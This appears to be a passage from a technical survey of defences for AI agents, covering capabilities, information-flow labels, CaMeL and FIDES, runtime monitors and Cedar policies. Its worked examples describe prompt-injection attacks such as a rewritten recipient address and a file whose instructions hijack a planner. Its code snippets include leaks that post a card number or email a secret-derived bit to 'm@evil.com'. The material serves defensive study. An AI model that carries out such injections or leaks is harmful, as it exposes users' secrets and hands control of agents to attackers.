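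### What the experiments found

Odersky and colleagues tested TACIT on a software project with a folder of passwords and confidential documents. They paired each of 12 ordinary tasks with each of 10 prompt injections, and added 11 tasks in which the user asked for the secrets outright or posed as someone entitled to them. This gave 131 trials for each of two models. They ran every trial with and without the `Classified` wrapper and checked whether any secret appeared in the agent's output.

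| Model | No leak, with wrapper | No leak, without wrapper |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 100% | 98.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 100% | 91.6% |

Without the wrapper, MiniMax leaked secrets in eight of the 11 malicious tasks and after three of the 120 injections. Claude leaked secrets in two of the malicious tasks and after none of the injections. The perfect scores with the wrapper are expected from its design, so they mainly show that the implementation works.

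The wrapper didn't make the agents less useful. MiniMax completed 90.0% of the ordinary tasks with it and 88.3% without it. Claude completed 99.2% with it and 83.3% without it. Claude's rate was lower without the wrapper partly because it sometimes stopped to warn the user when it noticed an injection.

Agents writing Scala did about as well at other work as agents using ordinary tool calls, even though few programs in their training data use capture checking. On τ²-bench, a test of simulated customer service for an airline and a shop, three models scored 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher with Scala. On SWE-bench Lite, which has 300 real software bugs, MiniMax fixed 41.7% with Scala and 43.3% with ordinary tools, a difference of five bugs. At most 7.9% of the programs written for τ²-bench needed a retry, and those usually compiled after one or two more attempts.

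TACIT also blocked all but one of 1,926 attacks on AgentDojo, across two models. In the exception, the user asked for a booking at one hotel, and an injected review recommended another. The agent booked the requested hotel but quoted the reviews, and AgentDojo counted the attack as successful because the other hotel's name appeared in the answer. TACIT's policy allowed the agent to show reviews to the user, so the agent did not misuse any capability.

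The AgentDojo results are weaker evidence for the type system than they seem. The agents' instructions for this test include a warning that side effects inside `map` happen immediately, which suggests the purity rule didn't apply to all the adapted tools. Much of the protection probably came from keeping outside text, such as emails and reviews, wrapped so that the main agent didn't read it.

Odersky and colleagues say TACIT's usefulness on AgentDojo is comparable to that of CaMeL, a system that tracks where data comes from. This overstates TACIT's usefulness with one of the two models, o4-mini-high, which completed 52.9% of the office tasks with TACIT and 81.4% with CaMeL.

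### What TACIT doesn't guarantee

A pure function can still leak a secret through its running time. Odersky and colleagues leave such covert channels out of scope.

The guarantee also doesn't cover programs written in other languages. If TACIT lets the agent run Git, the Scala compiler can't control what Git does. Odersky and colleagues recommend allowing only a few specific commands and running the whole system in a sandbox.

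TACIT also does not check that a permitted action is the right one. An agent with a capability to issue refunds can still refund the wrong customer, by mistake or because of a misleading bug report.

Some of the trusted parts also need more assurance. Researchers have proved that the core of capture checking is sound, using machine-checked proofs, but nobody has yet proved that safe mode is sound. The library of about 1,000 lines also has to be correct.

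The local model must retain nothing between requests. Otherwise the agent could give it a classified document and later send an ordinary query about that document, and the model would return the answer without a wrapper. An injection in the document could also make the local model write a false summary, which would remain secret but mislead the user.

### Checking capabilities while the agent runs

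Other designs do all their checking at run time, so agents can keep using ordinary tool calls. *Agent libOS* (Zhang, 2026) presents a system for agents that change after deployment by learning new skills, writing their own tools or starting other agents. A new tool lets the agent request more kinds of actions but gives it no new rights. If the agent writes a tool that deletes files, the system checks just before each deletion that the agent holds a matching capability and that the deletion is within the limits set for the task. A person's approval can't replace a missing capability.

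Suppose the agent saves its state, the shop revokes its access to the payment records, and the agent then restores the saved state. In a carelessly designed system, the agent would regain that access. Agent libOS compares the restored capabilities with the current ones and drops any that the shop has revoked.

In 33 scripted tasks run on Agent libOS, 119 actions took place and none was unauthorised. When Zhang removed the rule that a new agent gets only a narrowed copy of its parent's authority, one unauthorised action got through. A simple wrapper around the tools let through 20. These scripts test the software rather than a model's judgement. Zhang also ran 12 longer workflows with a real model, and all finished safely and correctly, but that is a small sample from one model. The trusted computing base is large and includes the Python interpreter, the database and the host's operating system.

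*AgentCap* (Suresh and Gao, 2026) issues a signed capability for each tool call. In its banking example, permission to send money lasts 30 seconds and covers one payment, and the recipient must appear in a trusted source such as the user's request. On AgentDojo, AgentCap reduced the attack success rate from 33.2% to zero with GPT-5.4, and from 45.6% to 5.1% with GPT-4o.

The policy and the attacks were the same for both models, so the count of zero successful attacks on GPT-5.4 depends partly on that model's behaviour. Some attacks on GPT-4o succeeded because the policy left certain values or data fields unprotected. The same gaps were present for GPT-5.4, but no attack succeeded through them in the single test run.

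Run-time checks can respond to events such as the user cancelling a task. Before a piece of code runs, a compiler can establish that all of it is free of side effects, which is hard to do by checking one action at a time. The two methods work well together, and TACIT already uses run-time checks for file paths.

### What if people grant too much?

Capabilities protect the shop only if it grants few of them, but people often can't predict which ones a task will need. According to *PRISM* (2026), mainstream agent systems give the agent access to every connected tool at the start of a session. A user study in *Towards Automating Data Access Permissions in AI Agents* (2025) found that people also grant agents too many permissions.

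One extra or missing permission can make an agent unsafe or unusable. When Tran-Truong and colleagues added a single outside web address to DelegateGuard's grants for convenience, 30 of 45 attacks succeeded, even though the monitor worked as designed. When they left out the permission to send data, the monitor blocked all 45 legitimate tasks.

Software might choose permissions better than people. Companies usually give employees permissions by role, because nobody has time to change them for every task. *Empirical Evaluation of Task-Based Permission Scoping Architecture for AI Agents* (2026) points out that an agent's task arrives as text, so a program can work out the permissions for each task. *PRISM* proposes removing tools in a test environment that can be reset, and checking whether the agent still finishes the task.

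Language models aren't yet reliable at deciding what authority an agent needs. *Task-Conditioned Least-Privilege Learning for Executable Terminal and MCP Agents* (2026) cites a benchmark, AuthBench, in which leading models withheld permissions that a task needed and granted others that it didn't. It also reports that an Anthropic classifier for judging proposed actions missed 17% of 52 cases in which an agent was about to overstep.

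Suresh and Gao compared their handwritten policies with those of Progent, a system in which the model generates the policy. Under attack, GPT-4o completed 74.9% of AgentDojo's tasks with the handwritten policies and 59.6% with Progent's, which often blocked legitimate values that the model hadn't predicted.

There may also be no single smallest set of permissions. To tell a customer that the refund bug is fixed, for example, the agent could use either the shop's email account or its customer-support system, and neither permission includes the other. *Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization* (2026) recommends showing such alternatives to the person who approves the grant. A simple risk score can hide the difference between them. On Microsoft's scale, for instance, a grant that reaches 355 functions of its online services can have the same level as one that reaches 11.

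Automatic narrowing can still be worthwhile if the program doing it can only remove permissions from a set that a person has approved. If it misjudges what the agent needs, it either leaves the agent with extra permissions that the person had approved or blocks some work until someone grants more. The program should read only the user's request, since a prompt injection in other text could cause it to keep a dangerous permission.

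Users also need a way to correct permissions they have already given. *How Agents Ask for Permission* (2026) surveyed 21 papers and open-source systems and found that few let users edit or revoke them.

The shop could start by letting its agent read the code, run the tests and submit a change. If the agent needs to examine the payment in the bug report, the shop can grant read access to that one record until the task ends. The shop never has to let the agent issue refunds, because fixing the refund function doesn't require sending anyone money.

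## Tracking where an agent's data comes from and where it goes

An agent that can't issue refunds can still do harm with what it reads. It might copy a card number from the payment record into its code change, or paste in an account number that a stranger put in the bug report. Most capability systems control which resources an agent can use but don't record where each piece of text came from. Information-flow control records this by attaching a label to each piece of data and passing the label on to everything computed from that data. It then checks the labels before an action goes ahead. TACIT's `Classified` wrapper is a simple label for secrets.

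### Labels and noninterference

Denning's *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* (1976) worked out the mathematics of such labels. A ⊑ B means that data labelled A may flow to a place labelled B. For secrecy, public ⊑ secret, so a program may copy public data into a secret file but not secret data into a public file. When a program combines data labelled A and B, the result gets their join, A ⊔ B, which is the least restrictive label that both A and B may flow to. A report that contains one secret figure is therefore secret. Labels ordered in this way form a lattice.

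Integrity labels record whether data is trusted and work the same way, with trusted ⊑ untrusted. A payment instruction based on both the owner's request and a stranger's email is untrusted. Labels can also list the people who may read a piece of data. If the owner and the accountant may read the payment records, and the owner and the lawyer may read a contract, then only the owner may read a text based on both.

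The strongest guarantee people want from labels is noninterference, which Joseph Goguen and José Meseguer defined in 1982. SRI, where researchers developed the theory, explains that one part of a system doesn't interfere with another if nothing it does can influence what the other later sees. For a program P, x ~ y means that the inputs x and y differ only in their secret parts. P satisfies noninterference if P(x) and P(y) have the same public output whenever x ~ y. For integrity, changing only the untrusted inputs must leave every trusted output the same, so a prompt injection can't alter a decision labelled trusted.

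A program can break this rule by copying a secret, which Denning calls an explicit flow:

```
card = payment.card_number
note = "Refund sent to " + card
post_publicly(note)
```

In an implicit flow, the program never copies the secret but lets it decide which lines run:

```
large = False
if balance > 10000: large = True
post_publicly(large)
```

The post reveals whether the balance is above 10,000 euros. An attacker who changes the threshold each time could work out any whole-euro balance up to a million with 20 such posts. A common defence is to label everything the program writes inside the `if` as secret. But when the balance is low, the program skips that assignment, so `large` stays public and the post still reveals that the balance is low. A checker that analyses the whole program before it runs can account for both cases, while one that only monitors the program as it runs can easily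 miss the skipped assignment.

Strict noninterference also forbids useful programs. Sabelfeld and Myers give the example of password checking in *A Model for Delimited Information Release*, since even the reply "wrong password" depends on the secret. Programs therefore need declassification, the deliberate relabeling of secret data as less secret. The shop might declassify the last four digits of a card to print them on a receipt. The rule has to specify which digits, because permission to release "any four" would allow four receipts to reveal all 16. The equivalent for integrity is endorsement, which relabels untrusted data as trusted.

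### Why language models are hard to label

In an ordinary program, we can see which variables go into each result. But a language model reads the request, emails and web pages in its context as one stream of text, and nobody can reliably tell which parts influenced a given word of its output. The safe rule is to label the output with the join of the labels on everything in the context, so after the agent reads one stranger's email, everything it writes is treated as untrusted. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues conclude that, from then on, that input must not be able to trigger any action with harmful side effects.

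Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, measured how enforcing the rule affects an ordinary agent running on GPT-4o. With no attacks, enforcement reduced the share of AgentDojo's banking tasks the agent completed from 98.8% to 37.5%, and the share of Slack tasks from 93.3% to 20.0%.

### The two-model design

One answer is to keep untrusted text away from the model that makes decisions. *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023) proposed splitting the work between two models. A privileged model takes the user's request and can call tools, but never receives untrusted text. A quarantined model reads untrusted text but has no tools. A controller, which is ordinary software, sits between them.

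Suppose the user asks for a summary of the latest email. The privileged model instructs the controller to fetch the email, store it as `$VAR1`, and have the quarantined model summarise it. The controller stores the summary as `$VAR2`, and the privileged model instructs it to display `$VAR2`. The privileged model receives only the variable names. An instruction in the email to delete the user's files reaches only the quarantined model, which can't delete anything.

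Willison allowed one exception, for when the quarantined model has to choose from a fixed list of categories. The controller can then check that the answer is on the list and pass it on. He called his proposal "pretty bad" because it makes assistants harder to build and less pleasant to use.

### CaMeL on one request

The two-model design also has a security flaw, which a Google DeepMind team pointed out in 2025 when it presented an improved version, CaMeL. *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* (Willison, 2025) describes the team's example. A user asks the agent to send Bob the document he requested at the last meeting, and says that the meeting notes contain Bob's address and the document's name.

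In CaMeL, the privileged model writes the whole plan as code in a restricted form of Python. It has seen only the user's request and the descriptions of the tools. The plan looks roughly like this:

```
notes    = find_notes("last meeting")
name     = ask_quarantined("Which document did Bob want?", notes)
address  = ask_quarantined("What is Bob's email address?", notes)
document = fetch(name)
send(document, to=address)
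```

A special interpreter then runs the plan:

1. It fetches the notes and labels them with their source.
2. It has the quarantined model extract the name and the address. Both come from the notes, so both inherit the notes' label.
3. It fetches the document, whose label also records who may read it.
4. Before sending, it checks a policy. A suitable one is that the recipient must come from a trusted source or already have permission to read the document. If neither is true, the interpreter blocks the email or asks the user.

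Suppose an attacker has replaced Bob's address in the notes with their own. The plan stays the same, because the privileged model never reads the notes. In the original two-model design, the controller would still send the document to the attacker, because the quarantined model returned the wrong address. CaMeL's policy check would block this. However, the attacker could change the document's name instead, and Bob would receive the wrong file, though only one he is allowed to read.

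The CaMeL team says that its approach "effectively solves" AgentDojo. Later tests support this for security, but they also show that CaMeL can fail many ordinary tasks. *SecureClaw* (2026) tested CaMeL on the full benchmark and reports that none of the 629 attacks succeeded, but that CaMeL completed only 29 of the 97 ordinary tasks. Some of these failures may come from the adapters needed to connect CaMeL to the test. In the comparison with TACIT, CaMeL completed 81.4% of the office tasks, so its completion rate depends heavily on the model, the tasks and the set-up.

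One practical problem is that the plan must process results the model hasn't seen. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026), which extends CaMeL to groups of agents, had to add a description of what every tool returns.

### FIDES and later systems

In FIDES, a system that Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, the agent chooses one tool call at a time instead of following a plan fixed in advance. When a tool returns data with a more restrictive label than the agent's context, FIDES hides that data in a variable and shows the agent the rest. The agent has two ways to learn what a variable contains.

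In FIDES, an agent can ask a quarantined model a question about a variable's contents and restrict the answer, for example to yes or no. The label records how much information the answer can carry, so a policy can allow one untrusted bit where it would block untrusted text. The agent can also open the variable, but its context then becomes untrusted and FIDES blocks most consequential actions.

FIDES checks two main rules before a tool call. A consequential action, such as a payment, requires a trusted context. Data may leave only if every recipient is allowed to read it. With these checks on, Costa and colleagues found no genuine successful attacks, compared with 152 against an unprotected agent. With GPT-4o, FIDES completed 41% to 59% of the tasks across the four settings, on average 8 percentage points more than an ordinary agent under the same checks. With o1, a stronger model, the advantage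 was 16 points.

The labels in this test were unusually good because the researchers marked every field that AgentDojo's attacks use as untrusted. A business would have to label its data without knowing where attacks will come from.

Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, built an agent called Randori in a new programming language where every value has a label, including the conversation with the model. Randori first practises its plan on artificial data, so it can fix errors without reading anything an attacker wrote. The plan may include endorsements, but the model has to write them before it sees outside data. Garby and colleagues also reran CaMeL on the banking tasks:

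| System and model | What has a label | Where the checks happen | Banking tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL, GPT-5.2 | each value in the plan | interpreter, before a tool call | 66.7% without checks, 37.5% with |
| FIDES, GPT-4o | messages, tool results and their fields | agent loop, before a tool call | 65.0% without checks, 52.5% with |
| Randori, GPT-5.2 | each value and the conversation | inside the tools | 75% with checks |

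There are only 16 banking tasks and the models differ, so small differences in score are weak evidence. Endorsement explains part of Randori's score. With another model, Qwen3.7-plus, removing endorsement reduced the share of tasks completed from 75% to 62.5%.

*Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) takes a less rigid approach, using a typed library to track labels. A model that has read untrusted text can keep calling tools as long as the labels permit each call. Garby and colleagues report that the agent completed 15 of 21 Slack tasks without the policies and 8 with them, while CaMeL completed 7.

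AgentDojo may no longer be hard enough to test these defences. In *Language-Based Agent Control*, every model resisted all 105 Slack attacks even with the policies switched off. The policies are still needed, because OpenAI's automated attacker, GPT-Red, consistently got past GPT-5.5's defences. Garby and colleagues also found that 97 of the 144 banking attacks needed an action that would never be in the plan for the user's task. A fixed plan generally stops such attacks without any labels, so the other 47 are a better test of label checking.

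### How often the agent has to ask

When a check fails, the system can request the user's approval instead of stopping. Users overloaded with requests approve unsafe actions, so a defence that requests approval less often is more useful and probably safer.

Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues argue in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) that most tests make information-flow control look worse than it is. These tests compare it with an agent that acts freely, whereas many real products ask for approval before consequential actions. Information-flow labels let an agent skip that request when an action provably follows the policy.

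They propose two measures. One is the total number of approvals needed across all the tasks an agent completes. The other, TCR@k, is the share of tasks it completes with at most k approvals each, so TCR@0 counts tasks done with no human help. On AgentDojo with the model o3-mini, the averages over five runs were:

| Agent | Tasks completed with no approvals | Total approvals |
|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent that asks before every consequential action | 24.3% | 48.2 |
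| The same agent with labels | 35.5% | 32.4 |
| FIDES | 50.1% | 18.8 |
| Prudentia | 59.1% | about 17 |

Prudentia is a version of FIDES that gives the model the labels and policies so it can plan around them. The model must justify opening a variable, and it can ask the user to endorse the contents first. If an email lists ten jobs that each need a consequential action, FIDES would open the email and then need ten approvals. Prudentia can ask the user to endorse the email and then do all ten. With o4-mini, Prudentia needed 19.2 approvals compared with 36.8 for FIDES, but it completed slightly fewer tasks overall (73.2% against 75.7%).

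The measures assume that people approve every legitimate request and refuse every attack. Endorsement makes this assumption riskier because a user who overlooks one malicious line in a long email turns it into a trusted instruction. Approving each action separately would give the user another chance to notice the attack. Kolluri and colleagues leave the design of these requests to future work.

### What the proofs cover

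Costa and colleagues prove that their label tracking can enforce explicit secrecy, which is weaker than noninterference. Explicit secrecy prevents a tool call from sending secret data directly anywhere the attacker can read it, but the attacker may still learn something about the secret from which tools the agent calls. For example, if the agent emails a supplier only when the shop's balance is low, the email reveals that the balance is low even if its text doesn't mention it. Costa and colleagues consider noninterference too restrictive, because after reading a secret the agent could hardly do anything that outsiders can see. Their proof treats the model as deterministic and leaves out timing.

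CaMeL has no comparable theorem, and Garby and colleagues found leaks in it. One uses the assignment that doesn't happen. A simplified version looks like this:

```
low, rich = True, True
if balance > 10000: low = False
if low: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

With a balance of 20,000, `low` becomes False and secret. The program then skips the assignment on the third line, so `rich` stays True and public. With a balance of 5,000, the program skips the assignment on the second line, so `low` stays public, and `rich` becomes False but stays public. In both cases `rich` reveals the secret, but the email is allowed because `rich` is labeled public.

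Garby and colleagues' language would stop a program that tried to change public state inside a branch that depends on a secret. Stopping reveals only about one bit of the secret per run. But in CaMeL, an outer loop that doesn't track labels restarts a plan after a failure, so an attacker could repeat the attack and extract the whole secret one bit at a time.

Their main theorem covers every program in the language, including code that the model writes during the run. Because a model's replies are partly random, the theorem compares the probabilities of what an observer sees from two starting points that differ only in data the observer isn't allowed to see. If every run finishes, the probabilities are identical. If some runs don't finish, the statistical distance between the two cases (a standard measure of how much probabilities differ) is at most the average of their chances of not finishing.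 With chances of 2% and 4%, for instance, it is at most 3%. A second theorem shows that endorsing untrusted data can't cause a secret to leak.

Lean checked these proofs, and they apply to the same interpreter that calls the model. They assume nothing about what the model writes, so they hold for any model. But their guarantees depend on someone labeling every source correctly and putting a check on every sensitive tool. The proofs assume that all the data sources are inside the program, which isn't true of a real bank or mailbox. They also don't show whether an endorsement was wise.

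### When the plan depends on what the agent reads

A plan written in advance can't include a job the agent discovers only by reading data during the task. Costa and colleagues count about 43% of AgentDojo's banking and Slack tasks as depending on data in this way, compared with 5% of office tasks and 10% of travel tasks.

Developers can write a plan with many branches, as *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) does for agents that operate a computer's screen. Its plans average 213 lines and 40 branches, compared with 52 lines and four branches for CaMeL's AgentDojo plans. But a plan can also become so flexible that it no longer protects anything. When asked to read a file and follow its instructions, CaMeL's planner wrote a loop that read each instruction and called the matching tool. With policy checks off, this loop let whoever wrote the file control the agent.

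FIDES handles some of these tasks by restricting the quarantined model's answers. To add a meeting to the calendar, the agent can ask that model whether the emails contain a meeting request, and the yes-or-no answer reveals one bit of information. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues suggest a similar restriction for a programming agent, which would see a library's documentation only as a strictly formatted list of functions, with names of at most 30 characters. Willison doubts that this is safe, since a name like `run_rm_dash_rf_for_compliance`, which refers to the file-deleting command `rm -rf`, would fit within the limit.

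Harder tests suggest that the problem is general. *AgentDyn* (2026) tried five defences on tasks that require agents to adapt as they go, and every defence that used GPT-4o completed far fewer tasks than the unprotected model.

The shop's bug report is a difficult case because the fix has to depend on it, which makes the code change untrusted. A strict policy would never let the agent install the change. The agent can still submit it, and the shop can endorse it after reviewing it and checking a proof that it obeys the refund rule.

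### Label creep

Labels only become more restrictive as data mixes, so over a long job nearly everything can end up labeled secret and untrusted, a problem called label creep. *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) measured it in simulated systems of agents. The number of agents and the way they shared tools strongly affected how far labels spread, but no design prevented creep entirely. *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (2026), a survey, concludes that agents may become unusable without safe, automatic rules for declassification.

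Another remedy is to estimate which inputs influenced an output and drop the labels of the others. In a test with a small model, *Sightline* (2026) removed half of the unnecessary labels but missed a real flow in 3.9% of episodes. This method therefore loses the guarantee, because a wrongly dropped label can let an attack through.

*Ghost in the Agent* (2026) shows that data-flow trackers can both report false flows and miss real ones. In 140 scenarios where no data flowed to the action in question, FIDES wrongly reported a flow in 94. In 40 scenarios where data influenced an action only through the agent's decisions, FIDES missed the flow in 23, as expected of a system not designed to track such implicit flows. The paper's own system, NeuroTaint, did much better on both sets, with one false alarm and three misses. But in 14 scenarios where sources only covered similar topics, NeuroTaint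 wrongly reported a flow in all of them, and FIDES did in nine.

The cautious label seems worth the inconvenience for an irreversible action such as a payment. An estimate is easier to justify for a draft that a person will read before sending.

### Text that misleads within the rules

Untrusted text can also do harm without causing any forbidden flow, like the false summary that an injection could make TACIT's local model write.

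Attacks on Randori succeeded in two of 1,296 runs, both with the same combination of task and attack. The user asked the agent to pay a bill as described in a file, and the attacker had replaced the file with a different bill. The plan endorsed the file's contents because the task required it. CaMeL failed on the same case, which its developers consider outside the attacks it is meant to stop. In CaMeL's other failure, the agent quoted a hotel review to the user, like the one TACIT let through.

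A stricter policy can block the false bill by requiring the recipient and amount to come from a trusted source. Randori did block it when endorsement was off, but then couldn't pay genuine bills from files either. The label records only that the payment details came from the file, so someone who knows what the shop owes has to check them.

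## Checking each action against a written policy

The shop can write down part of what it knows about its bills as a policy, such as a rule that payments may go only to suppliers on a list. A reference monitor can then check every payment the agent attempts against that list, which is called runtime enforcement. The monitor checks the agent's actions in order, allows those that follow the policy, and stops the first one that would break it. A policy can also depend on the agent's earlier actions.

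### A policy as a small automaton

Suppose the agent may not send a message outside the company after it has read a customer file. The monitor has to store only one fact, so we can describe it as a two-state automaton that starts in the state "unread".

| State | Agent reads a customer file | Agent sends a message outside | Agent does anything else |
|---|---|---|---|
| unread | allow, go to "read" | allow | allow |
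| read | allow | refuse | allow |

In one run, the agent runs the tests, emails the payment provider a question, reads a customer file and messages the owner. The automaton moves to the "read" state at the third action. The only action after that is an internal message, so the monitor allows all four.

In another run, the agent reads the customer file, runs the tests, and then emails the provider the same question. The automaton is already in the "read" state, so the monitor refuses the email even if it contains no customer data. The agent could have avoided this false refusal by sending the email before it read the file.

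The policy adapts an example from Schneider's *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000). Schneider warns that such an automaton works only if it recognises every way of sending a message. For the shop, those ways include requesting a web page with data in its address. The monitor must also keep its state when the agent restarts, or the agent could save its notes, restart and send them.

### Which rules a monitor can enforce

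Schneider proved that a monitor that can only allow an action or stop the program can enforce only safety properties. A rule is a safety property if every run that breaks it does so at a definite point. Formally, for any run that breaks the rule, there is some number i such that every run with the same first i actions also breaks it. In the second run above, i is 3, because nothing the agent does after its third action can take the email back.

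A monitor cannot enforce the rule "every customer who is owed a refund eventually gets it," because the rule is not a safety property. However long a customer has waited, the refund could still come tomorrow, so the monitor never reaches a point where it should intervene. A monitor also cannot enforce noninterference exactly, because noninterference compares runs that have different secrets and a monitor observes only one run. It can enforce a stricter rule that implies noninterference, but it will then refuse some harmless actions.

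Even some safety properties are unenforceable. A late refund breaks the rule "refund within three days" at a definite moment, but the monitor can't keep the deadline from passing. If the rule instead limits the number of program steps, the monitor can stop the program before it exceeds the limit.

Monitors can enforce more policies if they can alter what the program does. *Enforcing Non-safety Security Policies with Program Monitors* (Ligatti, Bauer and Walker, 2005) studies monitors that can hold back actions and insert others. Suppose every refund needs an entry in the accounts, which the program makes after paying. This rule isn't a safety property, because the later entry repairs the violation. The stronger monitor holds the refund back, tells the program that the refund went through, and releases both actions once the entry arrives, so no money leaves if the entry never comes.

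This trick fails when the program needs a response from outside. Ligatti and colleagues point out that a monitor can't pretend to send an email and then wait to see what the program does with the reply. Much of an agent's work depends on such responses, so monitors for agents mostly return an error message or ask a person for approval.

### Rule languages for agents

Wang, Poskitt and Sun (2025), in *AgentSpec*, present a language in which each rule has an event, a condition and a response. The shop could use it to require approval for any change to its refund code:

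```
rule @protect_refunds
trigger SubmitChange
check changes_refund_code
enforce user_inspection
end
```

Someone has to write the condition as an ordinary Python function. Other possible responses are to stop the agent, run a fixed action, or have the model reconsider. If the model reconsiders, the protection depends on the model again.

Wang and colleagues tested handwritten rules on 750 requests for risky code. The agent tried to run code in 422 cases, and the rules flagged 333 of them, or 79%. The paper's headline figure is over 90%, which matches the data if we leave out two categories where the agent's code did not contain the flaw. The researchers judged 58 of the flagged programs harmless, so about one in six flags was a false alarm.

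For a simulated household robot, the rules stopped every hazardous task, such as pouring water onto a laptop. The share of safe tasks the robot completed fell from 58.6% to 54.3%. Evaluating the rules' conditions took under 3 milliseconds on average, while the code agent's runs averaged 25 seconds.

OpenAI's o1 wrote rules that caught 87% of the risky code in cases it had not seen. Its rules for a robot missed 29% of the hazards, and one rule banned all pouring, even to water a plant.

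Suresh and Gao compared their policies with those of *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025), in which a model writes a new policy for every task. The model writes the first version from only the user's request and the list of tools, so an injection can't influence that version. Each rule in the policy allows or forbids calls to a tool when the arguments meet certain conditions. Progent blocks any call that no rule allows.

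The policy may have to change as the agent learns more. Suppose an agent that may message anyone in the company learns that Anna is handling the bug. The model then proposes allowing messages only to Anna. An SMT solver searches for a tool call that the new policy allows and the old one doesn't. It finds none, so Progent applies the change automatically. If an injection leads the model to propose allowing payments to a stranger, the solver finds such a payment and the change needs approval. The model therefore can't expand the agent's permissions without approval.

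Progent reduced attack success from 39.9% to 1.0% on AgentDojo with GPT-4o, and from 70.3% to 3.9% on another benchmark, ASB. But these figures provide little evidence about the guarantee, because the researchers simulated a careless user by having the software approve every policy change. The results mainly show that GPT-4o writes good policies. Without any later changes, the first policy reduced attack success on AgentDojo to 2.5%. When a careful person reviewed the policies, no attack succeeded, and only 6% of changes needed a decision.

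Shi and colleagues report that agents were about as useful with Progent as without it, but Suresh and Gao found that it often blocked legitimate values. Progent also doesn't cover attacks on the agent's written answers, a gap that *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) lists among its main limitations.

### Cedar

Cedar, an open-source policy language from AWS, allows a request only if at least one `permit` rule matches and no `forbid` rule does. The language omits general loops and side effects so that a solver can analyse policies exactly (Cutler, Disselkoen and colleagues, 2024, *Cedar*). The team modelled the language in Lean and proved its main properties there. They wrote the production version separately in Rust, and they test it against the Lean model on random inputs. The Rust version was at least 28 times as fast as two competing systems.

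The analysis covers every possible request. In an example from AWS's *Why Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore chose Cedar for securing agentic workflows*, a policy gives bulk discounts except on limited editions. Someone adds a condition to the exception that limits it to orders of more than 200 items. The solver shows that the new policy allows more than the old one, such as a discount on 73 limited-edition items, even though the added condition makes it look stricter. Answering questions like this took 75 milliseconds on average in tests by Cutler and colleagues.

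*How We Built Cedar* (2024) explains that Cedar ignores any rule that produces an error. A `forbid` rule that refers to a missing field would therefore block nothing. Cedar's validator finds most such mistakes before the policy goes into use.

In March 2026, AWS's *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available* (2026) announced a service that checks agents' tool calls against Cedar policies. Administrators can describe a policy in plain English, and a model translates it into Cedar. A solver then looks for likely errors, such as a rule that requires a customer to be both "gold" and "platinum". *AutoCedar* (2026) also pairs a model with a verifier to write Cedar policies. This kind of checking finds contradictions but not wrong numbers. If an administrator asked for a limit of 100 euros and the model wrote 1,000, the policy would still be consistent.

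Cedar also keeps no record of earlier requests. To enforce the rule about customer files, other software has to record that the agent has read one and attach this fact to every later request. That software then becomes part of the trusted computing base.

Some of the facts in a request may come from the agent. One of AWS's sample policies forbids refunds more than 90 days after the order, but it takes the order date from the tool call, which the model wrote. If the model gets the date wrong, or copies a false one from a prompt injection, a late refund can pass the check. To prevent this, the refund tool has to look up the real date.

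### Checking a whole plan before it runs

A monitor that checks one step at a time might not step in until earlier steps have done some damage. In *Guardians of the Agents*, Meijer (2025) proposes that the agent write its whole plan as a small program, which runs only if a verifier accepts it.

Meijer (2026), in *Return of the Theorem*, applies this to a car dealer's chatbot that a customer talked into selling a car for $1. The dealer writes its business rules as logical formulas, which define the set of permitted sales, each with a customer, a model and a price. The agent's plan defines the set of sales it could make, and an SMT solver looks for one that the rules don't permit. If the lowest permitted price is $30,000, the $1 sale is a counterexample and the plan doesn't run. If the solver shows that no counterexample exists, every sale the plan could make is permitted.

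The rules must also limit side effects. An agent that must delete `foo.txt` and `bar.txt` might plan to delete every file ending in `.txt`, which would remove both. Meijer therefore adds a condition that all other files must remain.

Like other sound checkers, the solver may reject a safe plan, and Meijer would then have the agent write another. But he gives no figures for how many real tasks agents can complete this way, and CaMeL's results suggest that the checks can greatly reduce that number. Meijer accepts that some checks can't be done until the plan runs.

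### Shields and backup controllers

Stopping is usually safe for an office agent, but a robot or a car may need to do something else. In reinforcement learning, where a program learns by trial and error from rewards, researchers can work out the safe choices in advance from a model of the environment. Alshiekh and colleagues introduced this method, called shielding, in *Safe Reinforcement Learning via Shielding* (2017).

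Suppose a delivery robot must never run out of power away from its charger. It has b units of charge, it is d steps from the charger, and each step uses one unit. States with b = 0 and d > 0 are bad. The state with b = 1 and d = 2 is also bad, because every step from it leads to a bad state. If we keep marking states as bad in this way until no more qualify, the remaining states are those with b ≥ d. From each of these safe states, the robot has at least one step that keeps it in the safe set.

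The shield offers the learned program only steps that leave enough charge to reach the charger. With 4 units of charge and the charger 3 steps away, it blocks a step away from the charger, which would leave 3 units for a journey of 4 steps. Shields can also enforce rules about sequences, such as never choosing a certain action three times in a row. *Verification-Guided Shielding for Deep Reinforcement Learning* (2024) describes how a shield can replace a forbidden action with a safe one.

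In experiments by Alshiekh and colleagues, programs with a shield always did at least as well as those without one, and most learned better. But the guarantee depends on an accurate model of the environment. If an old battery sometimes loses two units in a step and the model doesn't account for this, the robot can still get stranded. *Efficient Dynamic Shielding for Parametric Safety Specifications* (2025) is a recent attempt to make shields more adaptable. Shielding is harder to use for an agent that sends email and browses the web, because nobody has a reliable model of how people and websites will respond.

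The Simplex design, which Lui Sha and colleagues developed for control systems in the 1990s, pairs a complex controller with a simple, verified backup. The complex controller, which can be a learned model, normally runs the system. A switch hands control to the backup just before the system reaches a state from which the backup could no longer keep it safe.

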